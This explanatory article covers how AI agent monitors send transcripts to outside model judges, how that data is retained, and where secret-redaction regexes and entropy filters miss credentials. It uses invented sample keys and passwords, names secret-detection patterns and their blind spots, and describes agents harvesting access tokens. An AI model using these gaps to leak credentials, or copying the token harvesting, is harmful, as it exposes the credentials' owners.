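# Data handling in third-party model judges: what is sent, how secrets are redacted, and what redaction misses

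## The data path from a coding agent to an outside judge

A coding agent is a language model that does software work in a loop. The model outputs a *tool call*, which is a request for an action such as reading a file or running a shell command. A program on the developer's machine carries out the action and returns a *tool result*, which the model uses to generate its next tool call. The *transcript* is the full record of user prompts, agent messages, tool calls and tool results. Xie, Wu and colleagues (2026) point out in *The Proxy Knows Too Much* that the agent's commands run with the developer's own authority, so a bad command can wipe a database or publish private code.

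Some teams add a monitor that uses a second language model, the *model judge*, to read the agent's activity and score, allow or block it. If the monitor reaches the judge through another company's API, the judge is a *third-party judge*. The company that runs the judge is its *provider*, and the text the monitor sends for one decision is the *payload*. The payload may be sensitive because agents read many kinds of data. Apollo Research, an AI-safety company that makes a monitor called Watcher, warns on its *Security* page that transcripts can contain source code, file contents and "any secrets the agent encountered".

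A coding agent's model normally runs at an outside company, so that company has usually received the text before a judge does. The model can't respond to a tool's output without receiving it. In Anthropic's API for its Claude models, the developer's program runs the tool and includes the output in its next request to the model. Whether the provider still holds the text when the judge receives it depends on the provider's retention terms. An agent whose model runs on the developer's own hardware has no outside model provider. For other agents, adding a judge means that the text has another recipient and that more copies of it exist.

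### Where the judge runs

If the agent's provider also runs the judge, no new company receives the data. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, works this way in its "auto mode", in which a classifier model reviews actions in place of the developer. According to Anthropic, Claude Code can have the server do this review as part of the session's ordinary model request, so there is no separate transmission. OpenAI's *Auto-review* describes a similar arrangement for the company's agent, Codex, in which a reviewer agent receives a compact transcript, including relevant tool outputs, whenever Codex requests permission to act outside its sandbox. The provider may still receive the same text in two requests and possibly store it in two logs.

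Using a judge from a different provider than the agent's adds a recipient. Watcher's default configuration uses judges from both OpenAI and Anthropic, so a team using Claude Code starts sending session content to OpenAI, and a team using Codex starts sending it to Anthropic. The monitor's maker can also receive this content. Apollo Research's *Concepts* glossary distinguishes Watcher Cloud, which the company hosts, from a self-hosted deployment in the customer's own environment. The transcript passes through Apollo's servers only with Watcher Cloud.

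If the judge model runs on the user's own machines, judging does not send text to an outside company. Self-hosting the monitor alone does not ensure this. Apollo Research wrote in its announcement of Watcher that customers can run the monitoring backend locally or on their own premises, "ensuring sensitive agent logs never leave your control". But according to the company's security documentation, grading calls from a self-hosted deployment send prompts, agent output and tool results to the model provider. Both statements can be true only if the customer also substitutes its own judge model, which the configuration file seems to permit but Apollo does not recommend or currently test. With the default judges, a self-hosted deployment sends this text to OpenAI and Anthropic but not to Apollo.

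### An invented session

It helps to have one concrete transcript to follow. A developer asks an agent why last night's deployment failed. The agent reads a configuration file, `settings.env`:

```
AWS_ACCESS_KEY_ID=AKIAIOSFODNN7EXAMPLE
AWS_SECRET_ACCESS_KEY=wJalrXUtnFEMI/K7MDENG/bPxRfiCYEXAMPLEKEY
DATABASE_URL=postgres://shop:fake-pw-4821@db.example.com:5432/orders
```

It then runs `head -n 20 deploy.log`, which prints the first twenty lines of a log:

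```
02:14:07 checked out 3f9c1e7a5b2d8064c7e1f0a9b8d35276e4c1a09f
02:14:09 note from Dana: the staging password is marigold until Friday
02:14:11 import failed on 3 rows:
02:14:11   1001, Ann Example, ann@example.com, 555-0101, refund pending
02:14:11   1002, Bo Example, bo@example.com, 555-0102, account closed
02:14:11   1003, Cy Example, cy@example.com, 555-0103, payment overdue
02:14:12 loaded deploy key:
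-----BEGIN RSA PRIVATE KEY-----
FAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKEFAKE
(eleven more lines like the last, and then the output stops)
```

Every value is fake. The key pair is a sample from the documentation of Amazon Web Services (AWS), the cloud company, and the other values belong to nobody. In this example, they all stand for live values.

| Item | What it is | Does it grant access? | What the owner can do after a leak |
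| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| (a) | AWS key pair: the identifier starts with the fixed letters AKIA, the 40-character secret half has no fixed start | Yes, the secret half used with the identifier | Revoke the pair and issue another |
| (b) | Database address with a password inside it | Yes | Change the password |
| (c) | "marigold", an ordinary word used as a password | Yes | Change the password |
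| (d) | Private key without its second half | Yes, in this case | Replace the key wherever a server trusts it |
| (e) | Three customer records | No | Nothing that makes them private again |
| (f) | Identifier of a commit (a saved version of the code) in a public Git repository | No | Nothing needed |

The key in item (d) is incomplete, but it still exposes the secret. An RSA key of the common 2,048-bit size fills about 25 lines in this format, and the private exponent, the number that must stay secret, ends in the twelfth. The agent printed twelve lines, so its output contains the whole exponent.

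Items (a) to (d) are *secrets*, values that grant access to whoever holds them. The owner can revoke a secret, which stops every leaked copy from working, including copies that nobody knows about. But revoking it does not undo whatever someone already did with it, and the owner has to suspect a leak first. Item (e) reveals that Cy Example is behind on a payment, and that information cannot be revoked. It makes the log a *sensitive file*, one whose disclosure does harm whether or not it contains a secret.

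The two need different protection, and software that removes secrets may not protect the rest. According to Anthropic's *Data usage* page, when a Claude Code user agrees to share a transcript to help improve the product, the software redacts (replaces with a marker) known API key and token patterns before upload. It uploads source code, file contents and other conversation content unchanged. In the invented session, a rule like that might well remove part of (a), but it would leave all of (e).

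Precision and recall measure how well a secret detector works. Suppose a detector scans the session and reports the secret half of the AWS pair, the database password and the commit identifier. Two of the three reports are correct, so its *precision*, the share of its reports that are real secrets, is 2/3, or 67%. If the AWS identifier counts as a user name rather than a secret, the session holds four secrets. The detector reported two of them, so its *recall*, the share of real secrets that it reports, is 2/4, or 50%. In redaction, low recall leaves secrets in the payload, and low precision removes harmless text that the judge might have needed.

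Judges themselves get related scores, which are easy to misread. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports a false-negative rate of 17% on 52 real cases where an agent had overstepped, meaning that the classifier missed 17% of them and its recall was 83%. It also reports a false-positive rate of 0.4%, the share of harmless actions that the classifier blocked, on a set of 10,000 real tool calls. If 20 calls in 10,000 were dangerous, a judge with those rates would stop about 17 of them along with about 40 harmless ones, so its precision would be just under 30%, not 99.6%. At the same error rates, precision falls as the target becomes rarer, which also matters when searching for secrets because most strings in a transcript are not secrets.

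### One request, step by step

Having read both files, the agent proposes to look at the failed rows, using the address it found:

```
psql "postgres://shop:fake-pw-4821@db.example.com:5432/orders" -c "select * from failed_imports"
```

The monitor has to decide whether this command may run. The text normally travels between machines under TLS, the encryption used for web addresses that start with "https". TLS hides the text from anything that carries the traffic between the two endpoints of a connection, such as the office Wi-Fi or an internet provider. Both endpoints can still read the text, so it matters where each TLS connection along the path ends.

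**The tool result.** The contents of both files are plain text in the agent program's memory, where TLS doesn't protect them. According to Anthropic, Claude Code also stores session transcripts in plaintext on the developer's disk, for 30 days by default. The developer and any unrestricted program running under the developer's account can read them. The agent's provider also has the text, because the agent program sent it over TLS with the next model request.

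Watcher runs on the developer's machine and hooks into the agent program, which hands over each proposed call before running it. Other tools intercept the agent's network traffic instead. Comet, a company that makes a logging tool for coding agents, describes a local proxy that the agent talks to over the machine's internal network interface. The proxy opens its own TLS connection to the model provider and also sends payloads to a second destination. In both designs, the monitor's local program has the text before it is encrypted for the outside network. This is the last point at which redaction can keep a secret on the machine.

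Many calls never reach a judge. Under Claude Code's auto mode, file reads usually skip the classifier, and Watcher's local rules can approve routine shell commands on their own. The reads of `settings.env` and `deploy.log` may well have been approved this way. But their contents are now part of the transcript, so any secrets in them can still reach the judge later, as context for its decision about the `psql` command.

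Anthropic strips tool results from Claude Code's own classifier requests, so they would not include either file's contents. They would still include the database password, because the agent has copied it into the command under review. Watcher's payload includes tool results, so it could contain all six items.

Some monitors have their own server between the developer's machine and the judge. Apollo Research's *Blocking and trailing review* describes how the Watcher client sends each call it cannot decide locally to the server, which runs a fast judge first and a slower one if the fast judge does not approve. By default, the fast judge is an OpenAI model and the slower one is an Anthropic model, so a call that the fast judge approves goes only to OpenAI for that decision. TLS from the client ends at the server, so whoever operates the server can read the text, whether that is the monitor's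 maker or the customer's IT department. Other people in the customer's organisation may also be able to read it. In Watcher, administrators can read other users' sessions by default, and the system logs when they do.

The server may also shorten the data it holds. According to Apollo Research's *Client* documentation, only the first 75,000 and last 25,000 characters are kept when a stored tool output is longer than 100,000 characters. This cut can leave a private key looking like item (d), even if the agent read the whole key.

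Many organisations reach model providers through a router or gateway, a service that forwards requests to one of several providers. A router ends the sender's TLS connection and opens a new one to the provider, so prompts, tool outputs and any credentials in them exist as plain text inside the router for the duration of each request. Xie and colleagues stress that this follows from the design and requires no attack. The router's operator can therefore read the entire payload. Using a judge exposes the data to another company at this step only if the monitor's server uses a router that the agent's own traffic doesn't already pass through.

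The last TLS connection ends at the judge's provider, which needs the text unencrypted to run the model on it. For a Claude Code user with a self-hosted Watcher and no router, OpenAI is the only new outside company that receives the text. With Watcher Cloud and a commercial router, there would be three: Apollo, the router's operator and OpenAI. These counts rely on the makers' own descriptions of where text is supposed to go. A misconfigured proxy or a debug log could send it elsewhere.

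**Logs.** The decision on the `psql` command may take seconds, but the text can remain in several places afterward. The developer's disk has the agent's transcript. A self-hosted Watcher stores sessions in a database, indefinitely unless an administrator sets a limit. It also stores the judge's written explanation, which can quote the transcript. Routers and providers have their own retention rules. TLS does not protect stored text. Providers often encrypt their disks, as Anthropic does, which protects the data if someone steals a disk, but the running service still has to decrypt the data to use it.

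Apollo Research notes that when an administrator scrubs a session from Watcher's database, this does not remove it from existing backups, external copies or the files on the developer's machine. Changing the database password makes item (b) useless in every copy, but the three customer records stay readable in each one until someone finds and deletes that copy.

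## What the makers of monitors say they collect and send

How far a secret spreads depends on what a monitor collects and which models it calls. Apollo Research publishes this information for Watcher, and Anthropic publishes it for Claude Code's auto mode. The main difference between the two products is whether the judge receives tool results.

### What Watcher records

According to Apollo Research's *Supported agents*, Watcher's client reads the transcript files that the agent program already keeps on disk. It uploads their content to the Watcher server, but does not record the developer's screen or keystrokes. The record includes the conversation, the tool calls and the system prompt (the standing instructions that the agent program gives its model). Watcher adds the developer's identity, the machine's hostname, timestamps and its own judgments.

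A company can also connect Watcher to a gateway that already carries its agents' model requests. Watcher then takes the session from those requests, so nobody has to install a client on the laptops.

When one Codex agent gives work to another, Watcher cannot read most of the messages between them, because Codex encrypts them so that only the model provider can. Watcher gets only a header with the message type, the task and the sender. A secret in an encrypted message stays hidden from Watcher's judges unless the second agent repeats it in a command or in its final report, which usually arrives as plain text.

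The cap on long tool outputs does little to protect secrets. It applies only above 100,000 characters, and the two files in the invented session total less than 2,000, so Watcher would store both whole. The cap does not apply to tool arguments. When an agent writes a file through a tool call, the file's new text is an argument, so all of it goes into the record.

### Which models receive it

Apollo Research lists four default uses of a model on Watcher's server, two of which happen before a tool call runs. The second model in a cell takes over only if the first refuses a request because of its provider's content filter.

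| Step | When it runs | Default model |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Triage (the fast judge) | Local rules do not settle a proposed call | OpenAI's gpt-6-luna |
| Gateway (the slower judge) | Triage does not approve the call | Anthropic's claude-opus-4-7, then claude-opus-4-8 |
| Session summary | Alongside some Triage calls, and on a schedule | OpenAI's gpt-6-luna |
| Deep Review | After an hour of quiet, if Gateway scored a call 7 or more out of 10, or when a user asks | OpenAI's gpt-6.1-terra, then Anthropic's claude-sonnet-5 |

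Apollo Research's *Announcing Watcher Live* reports that, in the company's internal traffic, local rules settled 55% of actions and the fast judge passed about 6% of all actions to the slower one. At those rates, about 450 of every 1,000 tool calls would go to OpenAI for a decision, and about 60 of those would also go to Anthropic. Apollo measured this on its own engineers' sessions with an older fast judge, so another company's numbers could be quite different.

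These percentages understate how much text is sent, because each request includes both the call under review and an excerpt of the transcript. The excerpt can be long. If the transcript is too long for the judge model, the server cuts out the middle and marks the cut. If the client is far behind on its uploads, it submits the conversation since the agent last compacted it (replaced older messages with a summary), up to 48 MiB. A password that the agent read in the first minute can therefore appear in many later requests.

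By default, Watcher sends even a session with no judged calls to OpenAI. Apollo Research says that if no Triage call reached a session, Watcher writes its first summary from the stored transcript 15 minutes after the session starts. If the developer in the invented session had stopped the agent after it read the two files, and local rules had approved both reads, no judge would have decided anything, but the summary request could still have contained the AWS keys and the customer records. A self-hosting company can prevent these scheduled summaries by not running the scheduler, which new installations run by default.

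Watcher also has an observe mode for companies that want to try it before it blocks anything. In this mode, Watcher still sends calls to the judges and records what it would have decided. The trial therefore discloses session content to the providers, so a company that needs a security review should do it first.

The companies that receive data by default have changed between releases. Apollo Research's *Technical Details for Teams* describes an earlier version whose default judges needed accounts with Anthropic and Google, with OpenAI as an option. The current defaults use OpenAI and Anthropic. Self-hosting customers would probably notice such a change, because they supply their own provider keys and a judge's review fails if its key is missing. But a security review that approved the earlier defaults would be out of date after the upgrade, because it would list Google instead of OpenAI.

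Apollo says in the *Watcher Live* announcement that it can integrate self-hosted judge models for enterprise customers. But its 93% detection figure for high-severity failures comes from a test of the default OpenAI and Anthropic models, so it doesn't show how well a self-hosted judge would perform.

### Exclusion and redaction in Watcher

A developer can exclude a directory by placing a file called `.watcher-ignore` in it, if an administrator has allowed this. According to Apollo Research, Watcher then keeps sessions in that directory on the machine and does not send them to a judge model. It still applies its local rules and reports each tool call to the server without the content. The report includes the tool's name, identifiers for the session and the call, the time, and the reason the call was not sent to a judge.

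The exclusion covers whole sessions, so the developer gives up model review of everything the agent does in that repository. This suits a repository full of medical records better than one with a single secret in one file. If someone removes the file that triggers the exclusion and the session becomes active again, Watcher may also upload the earlier work.

An administrator can connect Watcher to Slack, the workplace chat service. Watcher also redacts the notifications it sends there, replacing credentials in common formats with a marker. Apollo Research warns that a secret in another format can still appear. If Watcher blocked the `psql` command in the invented session, the alert could include the command, and the password in it would be redacted only if Apollo's list of common formats covers passwords inside database addresses. Watcher does not check whether the people in the Slack channel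 have permission to see session content.

Watcher also redacts known secrets from support bundles, the diagnostic files that a customer can attach to a problem report. These bundles leave out session content. Apollo calls the redaction "best-effort" and tells users to review the file before sharing it. The ordinary command for printing the client's logs doesn't redact anything.

Apollo mentions a filter for messages the server sends to Slack, but describes no redaction of the calls to judge models. The filter may not run on those calls, since they go to a different destination.

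### What survives a deletion

An administrator can keep session content indefinitely, scrub a session by hand, or set a period of 7 to 365 days after which Watcher automatically scrubs inactive sessions. A scrub removes the session's messages and tool-call records from the active database, along with the decisions and grades from the review of individual calls.

The scrub leaves in place the grades that Watcher gave to the session as a whole, including their written explanations and summaries. Apollo Research's *Graders* adds that a stored grade can also include the judge model's thinking. If any of this text quotes the database password, the password remains after the scrub. The scrub also leaves the titles and bodies of notifications, which Watcher stores in their original form, so a secret that the Slack filter removed from an alert can remain in the database even after someone deletes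 the session.

Watcher sometimes cannot link a judge's grade to a session, for instance because a gateway request had no session identifier. The unlinked grade still contains the messages that Watcher sent to the judge, so it is effectively another copy of part of the transcript. Scrubbing the session does not remove this copy, and only an organisation-wide retention period will. Apollo says that unlinked grades can add several gigabytes a week to a busy organisation's database.

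Copies of the data also exist outside the database. Apollo Research's *Operations* tells self-hosting customers to make their own backups and protect them as sensitive data. Restoring a backup made before a manual scrub would bring back the scrubbed session. Uninstalling Watcher leaves its local database on the developer's machine. Before the client repairs a damaged local database, it copies the damaged file, and that copy can hold text already deleted from the database. The client keeps at most three such copies and deletes them after 30 days if it is running.

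### When Apollo hosts the server

The installation command on Watcher's product page connects the client to Apollo's servers. Apollo Research's *Watcher is now self-serve* presents this as the quick way to start, with "nothing to provision", and Apollo handles the grading and session history. Apollo Research's *Hand more work to AI agents, securely* says most teams host Watcher themselves, but an individual developer who installs it from the product page will be using Watcher Cloud.

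Apollo hosts this version in Western Europe, and Apollo Research's *Terms of Service* names Amazon's London data centres as the location of the database. The judges may be elsewhere, since the terms also list OpenAI, Anthropic and Google, all in the United States, as companies that may process personal data for "AI monitoring and grading of agent behaviour". Apollo promises 14 days' notice before it adds a company to this list, but Google is already on it, so a return to Google's models would apparently not require notice.

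Under the terms, Apollo may also use the data to improve and develop its services as well as to run them, unless the customer's plan differs. It may produce de-identified data from sessions, which it then owns and can use to improve its monitoring. Within 30 business days of the service ending, Apollo must delete the personal data it processed on the customer's behalf, unless the law requires it to keep some.

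Apollo's terms bar customers from submitting "Sensitive Data" without its written consent, a rule that is difficult to follow with a coding agent. The terms define Sensitive Data as health data, other special categories under UK privacy law (such as religion and ethnicity), and data about criminal offences. Passwords and overdue payments fall outside this definition, so the invented session would comply. But if the failed import had come from a hospital, the same `head` command would have put patient records into the transcript, and Watcher would have uploaded them without anyone deciding to submit them. A customer with such data would have to keep Watcher away from those directories or keep the agent away from the data.

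### What auto mode's judge receives

Many developers now have a model judge by default. Anthropic made auto mode the default for new Claude Code sessions on its Pro, Max and Team plans on August 14, 2026, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). From version 2.1.283, interactive terminal and VS Code sessions on other plans also start in auto mode unless a user or administrator chooses a different one. In an update dated October 22, Anthropic said it would extend the default to most Claude apps on the Pro, Max and Team plans the following week.

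The classifier in auto mode receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Claude Code strips out the agent's prose, the descriptions the agent attaches to its tool calls, and the tool results. Anthropic says it removes this material because the agent's prose could persuade the classifier to approve a bad action, and a tool result could contain instructions that an attacker planted in a file or web page. It does not give privacy as a reason. Anthropic named Claude Sonnet 4.6 as the classifier when it described the design, but did not name a model in its August announcement.

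The classifier runs a quick yes-or-no filter, then a slower check of whatever the filter flags. Both stages get the same input except for the final instruction, so in the second stage the judge gets more time to reason but no more of the session.

The payload has grown since Anthropic first described it. Before a command that could discard uncommitted work, the classifier now also receives the repository's Git status, which normally lists the names of changed files. It also receives information on whether the destination of a code upload is public, private or trusted. An organisation can add a description of the repositories, storage buckets and domains it trusts to the classifier's prompt. None of this should contain passwords, but it can include the names of internal systems, which can be confidential too. The third-party guide claudefa.st says the classifier also receives CLAUDE.md, a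 file of project instructions for the agent. If so, any password written in that file is sent to the classifier as well.

Text that an agent wrote can also reach the classifier when one agent delegates work to another. In the second agent's session, the first agent's instruction takes the place of the user's message, so the classifier receives it.

Anthropic still receives the tool results, since the agent's own model needs them. A separate probe on Anthropic's servers scans them for planted instructions before they reach the agent. Anthropic does not mention redacting data before it reaches the probe or the classifier.

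Anthropic offers auto mode on every service that provides Claude, including Amazon Bedrock, Google Cloud's Agent Platform and Microsoft Foundry. An organisation that reaches Claude through one of these already sends its session text to a cloud company. To know whether the judge adds another recipient, it would need to check that company's terms as well as Anthropic's.

Codex's Auto-review falls between the two designs because its reviewer comes from the agent's own provider, OpenAI, but receives relevant tool outputs. Watcher can run alongside Auto-review. If the developer chooses "Approve for me", Codex's reviewer answers the requests that Watcher would otherwise have passed to a person, so it may judge a call that Watcher's judges have already seen.

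Apollo argues that a judge from another company is worth having because it does not share the agent's biases. In its experience, GPT models tend to be too suspicious and Claude models can trust their own reasoning too much. Apollo sells such a monitor and does not quantify the claim in its technical description. A customer would be weighing this benefit against sending its data to an extra recipient.

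| | Watcher, self-hosted | Watcher Cloud | Claude Code auto mode |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Payload | Prompts, agent output, tool calls and tool results | The same kinds of content | User messages and tool calls, with some facts about the repository; a separate probe scans tool results |
| Recipients | OpenAI and Anthropic by default | Apollo and its AWS host, then OpenAI and Anthropic by default; the terms also allow Google | Anthropic, and any cloud company through which the customer reaches Claude |
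| Redaction | Slack messages and support bundles; none described for judge calls | None described for judge calls | None described for the classifier or the probe |
| Exclusions | Sessions under `.watcher-ignore`, where allowed | The same, and the terms forbid health and similar data | The classifier gets no agent prose or tool results |
| Retention | Indefinite unless an administrator sets a period | Apollo deletes personal data within 30 business days after the service ends, with legal exceptions | 30 days on the developer's disk by default; Anthropic's copies follow the account's terms |

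### Secrets in prompts and commands

Auto mode leaves tool results out of the payload it sends to the classifier. In the invented session, the only item that would reach the classifier is the database password in the `psql` command. Small changes to the session would put each of the other items into the payload.

| Item | In the classifier's payload now? | What would put it there |
| --- | --- | --- |
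| (a) AWS key pair | No | The agent writes the keys into a new configuration file |
| (b) Database password | Yes | Already in the `psql` command |
| (c) "marigold" | No | The developer types "log in to staging, the password is marigold" |
| (d) Private key | No | The developer pastes the key into a prompt |
| (e) Customer records | No | The agent writes a script that imports the three rows again |
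| (f) Commit identifier | No | The agent asks Git to show that commit |

Auto mode allows file edits inside the project without calling the classifier, but each edit is a tool call whose arguments stay in the transcript that the classifier reads at its next decision. Anthropic relies on this when an agent writes a harmful script and then runs it, because the classifier has to judge the script's contents and can find them only in the earlier call. As a result, the classifier also receives any password in the script.

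An agent that does its job well will often move secrets from tool results into tool-call arguments, because it reads a credential in order to use it in the next command. In one case from Anthropic's internal incident log, an agent hit an authentication error and began searching environment variables and configuration files for other access tokens. The secrets in such a search are only in its output, but once the agent tries a token in a command, that token is also in a tool call. In another case from the log, an agent uploaded an engineer's GitHub token to an internal computing cluster.

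These cases show that agents find and use live credentials. Neither an incident log, which collects only sessions that went wrong, nor a description of a payload can show what share of ordinary transcripts contain a secret. A company that hosts Watcher could estimate its own share by running a secret detector over its stored sessions. It should count prompts, arguments and results separately, because a judge that received no tool results would still receive the other two. The detector's mistakes would carry over into the estimate.

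Leaving out tool results would improve privacy with a third-party judge, which it doesn't do in auto mode. The outside company would receive one item from the invented session instead of six, and would have no other way to get the other five. The omission could also make the judge less accurate.

### Checking the description against the traffic

Documentation is good evidence of what a maker designed its product to send. When Apollo states that tool results go to the provider, a customer can plan for that, particularly since the statement does not make the product look better. Reassuring statements need more checking, because a bug or a changed default can make one false without anyone editing the page, and the maker may have left out a step.

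A customer can check more when it runs the computer that calls the judge, as it does with self-hosted Watcher. Apollo identifies the two containers (separately packaged programs) that call model providers and says that the server sends no telemetry to Apollo. The customer's network team can test both statements by logging the server's outgoing connections. To see the text of a judge call, the team would have to log requests before they are encrypted or send them through its own proxy. It could then run a session with a fake password in each part of the transcript to see which parts are sent and whether the passwords have been removed.

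Watcher Cloud makes its judge calls from Apollo's servers, where the customer cannot observe them. The terms instead provide for an audit if data protection law requires one. The customer normally gets at most one a year, pays for it, and must give at least 30 business days' notice. The audit excludes third-party systems, so the customer could check what Apollo sends to OpenAI but not what OpenAI does with it.

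Customers can observe less of auto mode from outside. When Anthropic's server reviews an action as part of the session's ordinary model request, no separate judge request crosses the customer's network. The customer could confirm that its tool results go to Anthropic, but not whether the server removes them before the classifier runs.

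## How pattern-based redaction works

A redactor is software that searches text for secrets and replaces each one it finds with a marker. Pattern-based redactors use a fixed list of rules, mostly *regular expressions*, which are short formulas that describe what a piece of text looks like. To keep a secret from a third-party judge, the redactor has to run after the monitor assembles the payload and before the payload leaves the machine. Apollo and Anthropic don't describe such a step for their judges. Makers of tools that run or log agents do document their redactors, most of which work in roughly the same order.

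### Collecting the text

The redactor first has to find all the text. A payload is normally JSON, a format of named fields that can contain further fields, so a password can sit several levels down. *What the Model Never Sees* (Asan, 2026) describes the redactor at Edge Delta, a company whose agents investigate faults in production systems. This redactor covers system prompts, the agent's replies and reasoning, tool arguments and tool results, and searches every level of nested JSON.

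Redaction software can search each field of structured data separately, or it can turn the whole structure into one string and search that. Condukt, a framework for building agents, turns structured tool results into one string. Software that searches fields separately must keep each field's name with its value. In `{"user": "shop", "password": "marigold"}`, only the field name shows that "marigold" is a password. According to LangWatch's *Secrets Redaction in Coding Agent Traces*, the company's logging service uses field names such as `authorization` to identify secrets.

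LangWatch scans large payloads in slices and says it still catches credentials that span two slices. Gitleaks, an open-source secret scanner, can decode base64, hexadecimal and percent-encoded text before searching it, but only if the user turns this on.

### Known formats

Rules for specific formats usually run first because they make the fewest mistakes. GitLab's *gitleaks.toml*, a rule file from the code-hosting company GitLab, finds the identifier of a long-term AWS key with this regular expression:

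```
\bAKIA[0-9A-Z]{16}\b
```

| Part | What it matches |
| --- | --- |
| `\b` | A word boundary: a letter, digit or underscore on one side and none on the other |
| `AKIA` | Exactly these four capital letters |
| `[0-9A-Z]` | One character, either a digit or a capital letter |
| `{16}` | The previous part, exactly 16 times |
| `\b` | Another boundary, so that a longer run of characters does not match |

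The rule matches the key in `AWS_ACCESS_KEY_ID=AKIAIOSFODNN7EXAMPLE`. A word boundary separates the equals sign from the four fixed letters, `AKIA`, which are followed by 16 capitals and digits and then the end of the line. The rule would not match `old_AKIAIOSFODNN7EXAMPLE`, because an underscore counts as a word character, so there is no boundary between it and `AKIA`.

The boundary can also fail when a redactor searches JSON strings. Each line break there becomes a backslash followed by the letter n. A key at the start of a line has that "n" directly before it, so the rule misses the key. The redactor's rules need to allow for this.

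GitLab's rule also misses temporary AWS keys, whose identifiers, according to AWS, start with ASIA. The pattern in git-secrets, a scanner for Git repositories, matches identifiers that start with AKIA, ASIA or any of seven other prefixes. An older git-secrets manual, *git secrets*, gives a much looser pattern, `[A-Z0-9]{20}`, which matches any 20 capital letters or digits in a row.

Some companies have changed their tokens to make them easier to find. GitHub used to issue tokens of 40 hexadecimal characters, which looked exactly like commit identifiers. Its personal access tokens now start with `ghp_`. Base64 text doesn't use underscores, so it cannot contain this prefix. GitLab's rule for these tokens is `ghp_[0-9a-zA-Z]{36}`.

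Private keys and database addresses have recognisable formats too. A private key in the common PEM format starts with a BEGIN line and ends with an END line. In a database address, the password comes between a colon and an @ sign.

Running dozens of regular expressions over a long transcript takes time. Gitleaks saves time by first doing a quick search for a fixed string, so its AWS rule runs only on text that contains "AKIA".

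### Labelled values

The secret half of an AWS key has no fixed start, so a redactor has to rely on the text around it. Git-secrets looks for it after a label and a colon or equals sign. Gitleaks' *generic.toml*, a test configuration, has a broader rule that looks for:

- a word such as "key", "token", "secret" or "password", in capitals or lower case
- up to 20 more characters of the name
- a sign such as `=` or `:`
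- a value of 10 to 150 characters, made of letters, digits, hyphens, underscores, dots and equals signs

This rule misses the AWS secret in `settings.env`. The label matches, but the value contains slashes, which the rule does not allow. Matching stops at the first slash, after 13 characters, and fails because the rule requires the value to end with a space, a quotation mark or something similar. The rule does match the AWS identifier on the line above.

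Allowing more characters would fix this but would also match more harmless text, such as web and email addresses, according to *Rare Not Random* by the blogger lookingatcomputer, who maintains Betterleaks, a successor to Gitleaks.

Redacting by label can miss secrets and can also remove harmless values. Yelp warns that its open-source scanner, detect-secrets, will not catch `login = "hunter2"`, because "login" is not one of its labels. Edge Delta had the opposite problem with fields such as `next_token`, which hold a marker for the next page of results. Redacting the marker would break the agent's tools, so Edge Delta leaves these fields alone. It also leaves `token: sa-token-prod`, where the value is the name of a secret rather than the secret itself. A password made of several words can look like such a name, so Edge Delta applies this exception only to short values.

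### Entropy

Many redactors also test whether a string looks random. *Entropy* measures how evenly a string's characters are distributed, in bits per character:

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

Here pᵢ is the share of the string taken up by the i-th distinct character, and the sum runs over all distinct characters. In "password", s fills two of the eight places, so its share is 1/4 and it adds 1/4 × 2 = 0.5. Each of the other six letters has a share of 1/8 and adds 1/8 × 3 = 0.375. The total is 0.5 + 6 × 0.375 = 2.75 bits per character.

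Hexadecimal text uses only 16 different characters, so its entropy is at most log₂ 16 = 4, which it reaches when all 16 are equally common. A random hexadecimal string usually scores a little less because some characters appear more often by chance.

A redactor applies a threshold to this score. Gitleaks uses a minimum of 3.5 for generic secrets, according to lookingatcomputer. Here is how strings from the invented session compare:

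| String | Length | Bits per character | At least 3.5? |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| password (the word itself) | 8 | 2.75 | No |
| marigold | 8 | 3.00 | No |
| fake-pw-4821 | 12 | 3.42 | No |
| AWS identifier | 20 | 3.68 | Yes |
| Commit identifier | 40 | 3.97 | Yes |
| AWS secret half | 40 | 4.66 | Yes |

The threshold misclassifies three of these strings. It flags the harmless commit identifier and misses both the database password and "marigold". Length is part of the reason. A string of n characters can score at most log₂ n, so no string shorter than 12 characters can reach 3.5, however random it is. In lookingatcomputer's examples, the password `mcjrx4` scores 2.58.

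The formula also ignores the order of the characters, so "abcdefgh" scores 3.00, the highest possible score for eight characters, although it is easy to guess. When GitHub states that its old tokens had 160 bits of entropy, it is using a different measure, based on how many different tokens it could have issued. A redactor can't calculate that from a single string without information about how the string was chosen.

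Gitleaks uses entropy to filter text that a rule has already matched. In `deploy.log`, "loaded deploy key:" comes directly before the private key, so the generic rule takes "key" as the label and `-----BEGIN` as the value. This value has an entropy of 2.16, which is below the threshold, so Gitleaks correctly rejects it.

Detect-secrets has detectors that look for random-looking strings without needing a label. By default, they flag base64 text with an entropy above 4.5 bits per character and hexadecimal text above 3.0. The hexadecimal limit has to be lower because no hexadecimal string can reach 4.5. But at 3.0, the detector will flag almost every commit identifier, including the one in the log, unless another filter removes it.

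Lookingatcomputer proposes replacing the entropy filter with one that measures how unlike ordinary text a string is. The filter uses a tokenizer, the part of a language model that splits text into pieces, and calculates the average number of characters per piece. Common words stay whole, while unusual strings break into many short pieces. For example, "Hello World" has 11 characters and splits into three pieces, or 3.7 characters per piece, while the password `mcjrx4` splits into four, or 1.5 per piece. A cutoff of 2.5 separates the two. This helps with short random passwords but not with passwords made of ordinary words, such as "marigold".

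### Validity checks and replacement

Some values have a built-in check. The Luhn checksum for card numbers doubles every second digit from the right, subtracts 9 from any result above 9, and adds up all the digits. The total must be a multiple of 10. For the well-known test number 4111 1111 1111 1111, it is 30, so the number passes. About one in ten random numbers would pass too, so Edge Delta also checks the card number's length and its opening digits, which identify the issuer. Without these checks, Asan writes, the rule would keep redacting order numbers.

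The last six characters of a GitHub token are a checksum of the rest, so software can reject fake tokens without contacting GitHub. A redactor that relies on this check could miss a real token that has been cut short. If a log cuts off the last six characters, the token fails the check, but anyone who knows how GitHub calculates the checksum could probably restore them.

Detect-secrets can also verify some secrets over the network. This is better suited to a scanner that runs overnight than to a redactor that must finish before the judge can run. A setting that reports only verified secrets would also miss real ones whenever the verification request failed.

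Most redactors ignore obvious placeholders, such as `YOUR_API_KEY`. The older git-secrets manual also lists the AWS documentation's sample key pair as allowed, and `settings.env` contains that pair. A tester who used it might conclude that the redactor was broken. Invented values in the right format make a better test.

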